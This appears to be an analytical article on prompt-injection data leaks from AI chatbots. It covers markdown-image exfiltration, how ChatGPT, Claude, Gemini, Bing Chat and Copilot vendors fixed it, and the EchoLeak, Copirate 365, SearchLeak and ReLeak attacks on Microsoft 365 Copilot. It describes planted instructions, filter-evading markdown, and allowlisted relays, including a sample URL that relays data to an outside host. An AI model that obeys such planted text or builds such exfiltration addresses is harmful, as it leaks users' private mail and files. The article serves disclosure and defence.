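An attacker with *n* indexed pages can extract up to log₂ *n* bits per request, which is about 5.2 bits with 36 pages and 10 bits with 1,000. A six-digit login code has a million possible values, so sending it takes four requests with 36 pages (36³ is 46,656, while 36⁴ is about 1.7 million) and two with 1,000. A 3,000-character conversation, sent one character at a time, would take 3,000 requests. The check therefore protects long texts much better than short secrets.

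Rehberger suggested storing each page for a few minutes or refusing to visit the same address twice in a session, so that an attacker could not reuse the page for "e" every time the letter occurred. He had not tested whether OpenAI already did this. Either measure would make an attack harder but not impossible, since an attacker with enough pages could use a different set for each position in the message.

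He calls the index check a significant improvement, but doubts that every OpenAI developer will know to use it. PromptArmor's *OpenAI API logs unpatched data exfiltration* gives an example, in which OpenAI's page for reviewing logs displayed markdown images unsafely. A developer who opened a suspicious reply there could set off the leak, even if the developer's own app had blocked the image.

Google has a simpler rule for images in its chatbot, Gemini. Google (2025) states that Gemini does not display images from external addresses, and that it checks links against Safe Browsing, Google's service for detecting dangerous sites. Safe Browsing is a weaker barrier to this kind of leak than an index of exact addresses, since an attacker's new and otherwise harmless site may not look dangerous. The image rule also did not cover Gemini's browsing tool. Tenable's *Gemini Browsing Tool* describes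 how planted text made the tool open an address containing the user's saved information and location. Google has since changed the tool to prevent this.

Anthropic limits the web-fetching tool in its chatbot, Claude, to exact addresses that the user has entered or that Claude's search tool has returned. Willison's *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* praises the design but reports that Ayush Paul found a hole in it.

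### How the vendors' repairs compare

*Trust No AI*, from December 2024, lists eleven products in which Rehberger had found and reported the image leak, five of them Google's. It also describes a close relative in Slack, Discord and Teams, which fetch a link automatically to show a preview and so can leak data without an image. The list does not reveal what share of chatbots had the flaw, because Rehberger gives no count of those he tested and found safe. For six products the dates and repairs are known:

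| Product | Reported | Fixed | Type of fix |
|---|---|---|---|
| Bing Chat | 8 April 2023 | 15 June 2023 | Browser rule allowing images from four Microsoft domains |
| ChatGPT | 9 April 2023 | December 2023 in part; stronger from about August 2025 | Check on each address before loading |
| Claude | 12 July 2023 | 26 July 2023 | User must click "Show Image" |
| Azure AI Playground | 24 July 2023 | 13 September 2023 | Added space that stops the image code from working |
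| Google Vertex AI | 30 August 2023 | 19 October 2023 at the latest | No images or clickable links |
| GitHub Copilot Chat | 25 February 2024 | 12 June 2024 | Images from trusted domains only (probably) |

Most dates in the "Fixed" column are when a vendor closed the report or confirmed the fix, which can be later than the fix itself. Rehberger has since dated Microsoft's policy for Bing Chat to May 2023, some weeks before Microsoft told him about it. Embrace The Red's *Google Cloud Vertex AI* says Google accepted the report in 22 minutes and probably fixed the flaw weeks before he asked in October.

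The cases also differed in urgency. Neither Vertex AI nor the Azure playground could fetch outside pages at the time, so a victim had to paste in the hostile text, and Rehberger rated both flaws as medium. Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed* describes a flaw in Claude, which was more exposed because it accepted uploaded files. Anthropic closed the vulnerability report in 14 days.

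Sources disagree about how GitHub fixed the flaw in Copilot Chat, an assistant for programmers. Rehberger tested the assistant in the code editor VS Code and wrote in Embrace The Red's *GitHub Copilot Chat* that the fix "seems to be" that it no longer displayed markdown images. Willison's *GitHub Copilot Chat* says that GitHub blocked only images from untrusted domains. Vulners' *GitHub*, an entry in a database of software flaws, supports Willison's account and adds that users now saw a notice about links.

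The strongest evidence is a later GitHub security advisory, *VS Code*. It explains that the editor's chat used a list of trusted domains to decide which remote images to show, until version 1.100.1 stopped showing remote images altogether. That version was a security update to Visual Studio Code's *April 2025 (version 1.100)* (2025) release. Willison's account therefore fits the 2024 repair better. Rehberger's observation also fits, because his own test server would not have been on the list.

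Copilot Chat on GitHub's website had the same flaw. Its policy allowed images only from GitHub's domains, but one of these hosted Camo, a service that fetches outside images for display on GitHub. Camo accepted only addresses that GitHub had signed in advance, which should have prevented anyone from adding stolen data. Legit Security's *CamoLeak* describes how a researcher obtained a signed address for every letter and symbol, then had Copilot spell out private code using one invisible image per character. By 14 August 2025 GitHub had turned off images in the chat completely.

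### What each repair costs the user

Removing images is the most secure of these repairs, and a programmer asking about code loses little without them. Rehberger called it probably the best possible fix for Vertex AI, which didn't need images. But a general chatbot without images can't show photographs of a holiday destination or diagrams from an encyclopaedia. A short allowlist such as Bing Chat's keeps the vendor's own images and requires no action from the user, but it blocks images from the rest of the web.

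The added space in the Azure playground has a similar drawback. It also depends on the filter recognising every way of writing an image, so it is a less certain barrier than a rule in the browser. Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Fixes Data Exfiltration Vulnerability in Azure AI Playground* infers this repair from what the program displayed.

With Claude's button, users could still view any picture, but they had to click first. Rehberger thought the fix was imperfect, though it stopped the automatic leak. Users had to decide whether a picture was safe before seeing it, and the planted text may have made Claude recommend it.

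OpenAI's index check leaves most of the public web open and interrupts the user less often than a button on every image. However, it can flag harmless links that a crawler has not seen, which would include many new pages and private links. The user may see the same warning for these as for a link carrying a stolen email summary, and must then read the address to work out which it is.

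## Microsoft 365 Copilot, 2025 to 2026: ways around the allowlist

Microsoft 365 Copilot is the assistant Microsoft sells to organisations for use in programs such as Word, Excel and Teams. Like Bing Chat after the 2023 repair, it had a Content Security Policy that allowed images only from listed domains. Researchers still found ways to get private data out and published four sets of findings between June 2025 and December 2026.

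### From one page to the whole office

Rehberger's Bing Chat attack could reveal the open page and the conversation. Microsoft 365 Copilot also searches a user's email, Teams chats, stored files and internal websites for passages relevant to their question, and adds them to the context before the model writes an answer. Developers call this retrieval-augmented generation, or RAG.

Copilot searches with the user's permissions, so an attacker who takes control of the model can have it look for things the user never mentioned. The search also gives the attacker an easier way in. Only employees can use an organisation's Copilot, but anyone can email an employee, and Copilot may later retrieve that message by itself.

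### EchoLeak: an email and a Teams service

Aim Labs, the research department of Aim Security, found the first of the four attacks in January 2025. The attacker could send the victim an email from any address. The victim only had to ask Copilot a question about their work that led it to retrieve the email, and didn't have to open the email themselves.

To make that likely, Aim Labs relied on how such searches usually work. A RAG system commonly converts each passage of text into a list of numbers, so that passages with similar meanings are close together, and then fetches the passages nearest to the question. A short email is close to only a few questions, so the team wrote a long one that repeated the same instructions under headings on different office topics, such as staff induction and leave, as Ravia explains in *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (2025).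 The team did not know the details of Copilot's search engine, but it still retrieved the email in response to questions on various topics.

The attack had to get past several defences. Microsoft used a classifier, a program trained to recognise prompt injections, to keep hostile text from reaching the model. Aim Labs worded the email as a request to its human recipient, without mentioning an AI, and the classifier let it through.

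Copilot also removed outside links and images from its replies, but its filter recognised only the usual way of writing them. Markdown has a second form, which puts the address on a separate line:

`![a sleepy cat][cat]`

`[cat]: https://example.com/cat.png`

The filter missed this form, but the Content Security Policy would still have blocked a request to Aim Labs' server. The image allowlist that Ravia published has 29 different entries, 11 of which admit every subdomain of a domain. The team searched the permitted domains for a relay, a service that fetches any address it is given. They found one in SharePoint, Microsoft's system for internal websites, but it worked only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. They also found a Teams service that worked without an invitation.

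Suppose that a policy allows images from pictures.example.org, and that this site has a service for fetching outside pictures. An attacker could have the model write an image address like this:

`https://pictures.example.org/fetch?address=https://example.com/sleepy`

The browser sends the request because pictures.example.org is on the list. That server then contacts example.com, whose log records the word "sleepy". In EchoLeak, the Teams service fetched the address, which contained whatever the model had selected as the most sensitive information in its context. The planted text also included a request that the recipient not mention the email, which kept Copilot from listing it as a source.

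The allowlist could be bypassed because a request to a Microsoft domain did not necessarily stay with Microsoft. According to the case study *EchoLeak*, Microsoft deployed a fix on its servers in May 2025 and published an advisory on 11 June. GCVE's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025) lists two severity scores: 9.3 (critical) from Microsoft and 7.5 (high) from the US National Vulnerability Database (NVD). Both judged that the attack was easy and required no user interaction. Microsoft's score is higher because the company also judged that the harm extended beyond the vulnerable component and that an attacker could alter some data.

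Ravia calls EchoLeak the first known zero-click AI vulnerability. Rehberger's 2023 attack needed no click either, so the claim holds only in the narrower sense Ravia also gives, that earlier attacks either required the user to point the chatbot at the hostile material or could steal only limited data. Rehberger's attack worked only if the Bing Chat user had the poisoned page open, whereas an EchoLeak victim might never have known that the email existed.

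### Copirate 365: fonts instead of pictures

In autumn 2025 Rehberger noticed that Microsoft 365 Copilot had begun to display small web pages inside the chat. Microsoft stripped image tags from these pages, but a web page can load outside material in other ways. Rehberger asked Copilot to write a page that used as many of them as possible. One method worked, because the style sheet, the part of a page that sets its appearance, could still request a background picture.

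The image allowlist limited where that picture could come from. Rehberger kept looking, again with Copilot's help, and found that a style sheet could also request a font. A Content Security Policy has separate rules for different file types, and Copilot's rule for fonts was looser than its rule for images. The browser would fetch a font directly from Rehberger's server, so he did not need a relay.

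Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* describes the complete attack, which began with a Word document shared with the victim. When the victim opened it and typed a greeting to Copilot, text planted in the document made Copilot search the mailbox for a particular email, create a web page and put the email's contents in the address of a font. Users normally had to click to preview such a page, but the planted text made Copilot open the preview itself.

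Rehberger reported the leak on 16 October 2025, and Microsoft closed the case as fixed on 5 March 2026. That took 140 days, about twice as long as the Bing Chat repair. STAR Labs' *CVE-2026-24299* (2026) and INCIBE's *CVE-2026-24299* (2026), a page from Spain's national cybersecurity institute, both record a score of 5.3 (medium). But Microsoft labelled the flaw "Critical", a rating it assigns separately from the score.

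The score of 5.3 is based on the attack being difficult and needing user interaction, while Rehberger calls it zero-click. Opening the shared document may have been counted as interaction. Rehberger treats that as normal use, which is reasonable for a program made for sharing documents.

Rehberger also showed how to make the leak persist across conversations. He planted instructions in a biography of Albert Einstein, and Copilot ended its summary by asking whether the information had been helpful. Answering either yes or no made Copilot save an instruction to its long-term memory. In later conversations, when the user pasted a password, Copilot put it in the address of a font. Microsoft reported the memory flaw fixed in December 2025. According to its documentation in April 2026, changes to Copilot's memory left no entries in the audit log, so administrators could not have checked the log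 for tampering.

The image allowlist varied with the application Copilot was running in, such as Excel or SharePoint, and some entries seemed to contain individual employees' usernames. Embrace The Red concludes that the policy "is not a reliable security boundary in Copilot". Bing Chat's 2023 list was much easier to review because it had only four domains.

### SearchLeak: an image that loaded too early

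The third attack began with a link to Microsoft's own website. The web address of Copilot's search page for organisations could include a query, which Copilot ran as soon as the page opened. An attacker could write instructions into a link and send it to the victim by any means. *SearchLeak*, published by the data security company Varonis on 15 June 2026, describes how one click made Copilot search the victim's mailbox, take the subject line of an email and put it in the address of an image. Subject lines often contain login codes, as the one in the demonstration did.

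To block images in Copilot's output, Microsoft wrapped the finished reply in a code block, which makes the browser display the text without interpreting it. But Copilot showed the reply while the model was still writing, and the wrapping came only at the end. By then, the browser had already interpreted the image tag and sent the request.

The image allowlist still applied, so Varonis used Bing's search-by-image feature as a relay. The feature fetches a picture from a given address to analyse it. The browser contacted Bing, which then contacted the attacker's server.

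Microsoft's 4 June advisory, *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), scores the flaw 6.5, again labels it "Critical", and states that Microsoft had already fully mitigated it. The NVD scores it 7.5. According to Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails* (2026), the NVD assumed the attack needed no user interaction. Microsoft's score looks more accurate, since the victim had to click the link.

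Customers had nothing to install, and the advisory states that its purpose is transparency. The public record has improved in this respect since 2023, when Rehberger's account of the Bing Chat flaw had no CVE number.

### ReLeak: Bing again

Aim Labs became Cato AI Labs after Cato Networks bought Aim Security. On 3 December 2026 the renamed team announced three more attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot. *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) presents them as a sequel to EchoLeak. Like EchoLeak, all three began with an email that the victim did not need to open. Copilot retrieved the email while answering an ordinary question, and Microsoft's classifier again failed to stop the planted instructions.

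In the first attack, CVE-2026-124115, the model put confidential information in the address of a markdown image. The browser requested the image from Bing, which the allowlist permitted, and Bing's servers passed the data to an outside server. The team confirmed the leak when that server logged information from an internal email. Tamilselvan (2026) writes in *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaws Allow Zero-Click Data Theft* that the policy covered the image load but not the service's own network activity afterwards.

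Antipov (2026), in *Письмо даже не нужно открывать* ("You don't even have to open the email"), compares this channel to the one in SearchLeak, which required a click. The team sent Microsoft its three reports between 29 July and 20 August, so a Bing service could still carry data out of Copilot weeks after Microsoft had declared SearchLeak fully mitigated. Microsoft patched the image attack on 15 November. The attack had no confirmed public severity score when the researchers published, and Faisal (2026), in *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief*, notes that two of the three CVE records were still empty placeholders.

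The other two attacks did not depend on the browser. In one, Microsoft's background processing followed links in files that Copilot had created. In the other, code that Copilot ran escaped its network isolation and sent the data out directly.

To help find these flaws, Cato's researchers directed AI agents that wrote test cases, studied Copilot's refusals and adjusted the next attempt. Rehberger had used Copilot itself in a similar way. If a model can quickly list every feature that might contact an outside server, defenders can no longer count on an obscure gap staying hidden for long.

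### Why the allowlist did not hold

EchoLeak, SearchLeak and the image attack in ReLeak all got past the allowlist by relaying a request through an allowed Microsoft service. The browser enforced the Content Security Policy correctly and contacted only Microsoft, but the policy does not control what an allowed service then fetches. Security engineers knew this kind of relay as server-side request forgery long before chatbots. In Copirate 365, by contrast, the policy itself permitted the font request to a third-party server.

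Bing was on the Microsoft 365 Copilot allowlist that Aim Labs published in June 2025, a year before Varonis used Bing. The 2023 list for Bing Chat also included www.bing.com, the host of the image search in SearchLeak. Bing Chat was a different product, and Bing's services may have worked differently in 2023, so this is not evidence that anyone could have got data past the 2023 list.

Varonis advises security teams to review their allowlists for any domain that fetches addresses supplied by users. The advice is sound but hard to follow when one entry allows every subdomain of teams.microsoft.com. A reviewer would need to know about every service on those subdomains, and another team could add a new service after the review.

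Checking the whole web address would be stronger than checking only the domain. A check against OpenAI's index of addresses already known to its crawler should reject an address containing a stolen email, even if it begins with bing.com. Rehberger recommends this kind of check and does not think Microsoft's Copilots use one yet. Microsoft should already have a suitable index because it runs a search engine. The check would also have to cover fonts and anything else a page can load, or an attack like Copirate 365 would get around it.

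### Defending the model or the way out

Willison coined the term "lethal trifecta" for an assistant that has access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to communicate with the outside world. An attacker who can use all three can steal the data, and removing any one of them prevents the theft. Microsoft 365 Copilot has the first two because its purpose is to read a user's private files and incoming mail. Embrace The Red therefore argues that outbound communication is the only one of the three a company can realistically control, since no one has a deterministic fix for prompt injection.

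Aim Labs focused more on how an attack gets in. Ravia uses the term "LLM scope violation" for an attack in which untrusted text makes a model use trusted data without the user's consent. The narrower term is meant to help people build narrower defences, and Ravia recommends guardrails that detect such violations as they happen. Aim Security developed guardrails of this kind, so it had a commercial interest in the advice. Like other classifiers, these guardrails are vulnerable to an attacker who keeps rewording the text until it passes. Cato's own results in 2026 are another reason to doubt them, because Microsoft's classifier failed against all three attacks more than a year after EchoLeak.

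The four cases support Rehberger on what can be repaired. Microsoft can tighten a font rule or stop a service from forwarding requests, then test whether the route is closed. It has no comparable test for whether a model will follow instructions in the next cleverly worded email. But the defences meant to stop data from leaving also failed in all four cases, including the link filter, the code block and the allowlist. Each new ability, such as previewing web pages or creating files, opened another route for the data. In practice, "enforceable" has meant that Microsoft could close a route once somebody had reported it.

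SearchLeak is also a partial exception to the claim that software can enforce limits only on how data leaves. The instructions arrived in a link, and Copilot ran them as if the user had typed them. Microsoft could have put the text in the search box and waited for the user to press Enter. A careless user might still have pressed it, but the software would have enforced the pause whatever the text contained.

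Another option is to restrict what the model can read at one time. *EchoLeak* proposes access controls based on where text comes from and recommends keeping outside emails apart from internal documents. Labels in the context could not guarantee that separation. Software could guarantee it by never placing the two kinds of text in the same context, but Copilot could then no longer use the company's own records to draft a reply to a customer, which is much of what organisations buy it for. Stricter file permissions would interfere less with Copilot's usefulness and reduce what an attacker can steal, but both the employee and Copilot would still need access to the employee's email.

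Microsoft said in 2025 that it uses both a classifier, which was only meant to make attacks rarer, and deterministic measures, which limit the damage from attacks that get through. This position is close to Rehberger's. Microsoft's claim to have deterministically blocked leaks through markdown images is weaker, because ReLeak used a markdown image in 2026 and needed only a relay to avoid the block.

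Faisal quotes Cato's verdict that "too little progress has been made". That is fair for the classifier and the relays, since Bing served as a relay in two successive disclosures. It is less fair to Microsoft's handling of the reports, because Microsoft fixed each flaw before its details became public.

Looking back in 2026, Rehberger credits Microsoft as the first vendor to acknowledge and address the image leak, in 2023. He writes that the flaw has since become one of the most common in AI applications.

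### Exploitation outside research

No source reports that criminals or spies used any of the four attacks. Microsoft confirmed that EchoLeak had affected no customers, and CISA, the US cybersecurity agency, had recorded no exploitation as of 14 June 2025, three days after the disclosure. The records for Copirate 365 and SearchLeak also list them as not exploited. Cato knew of no affected customers when it published ReLeak.

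This evidence is better for EchoLeak, SearchLeak and ReLeak than for Copirate 365. The relays in the first three attacks ran on Microsoft's servers, so the company could have searched its own logs for suspicious requests, if it had kept them. In Copirate 365, the request went directly from the victim's computer to the attacker's server, so Microsoft was less likely to see it.
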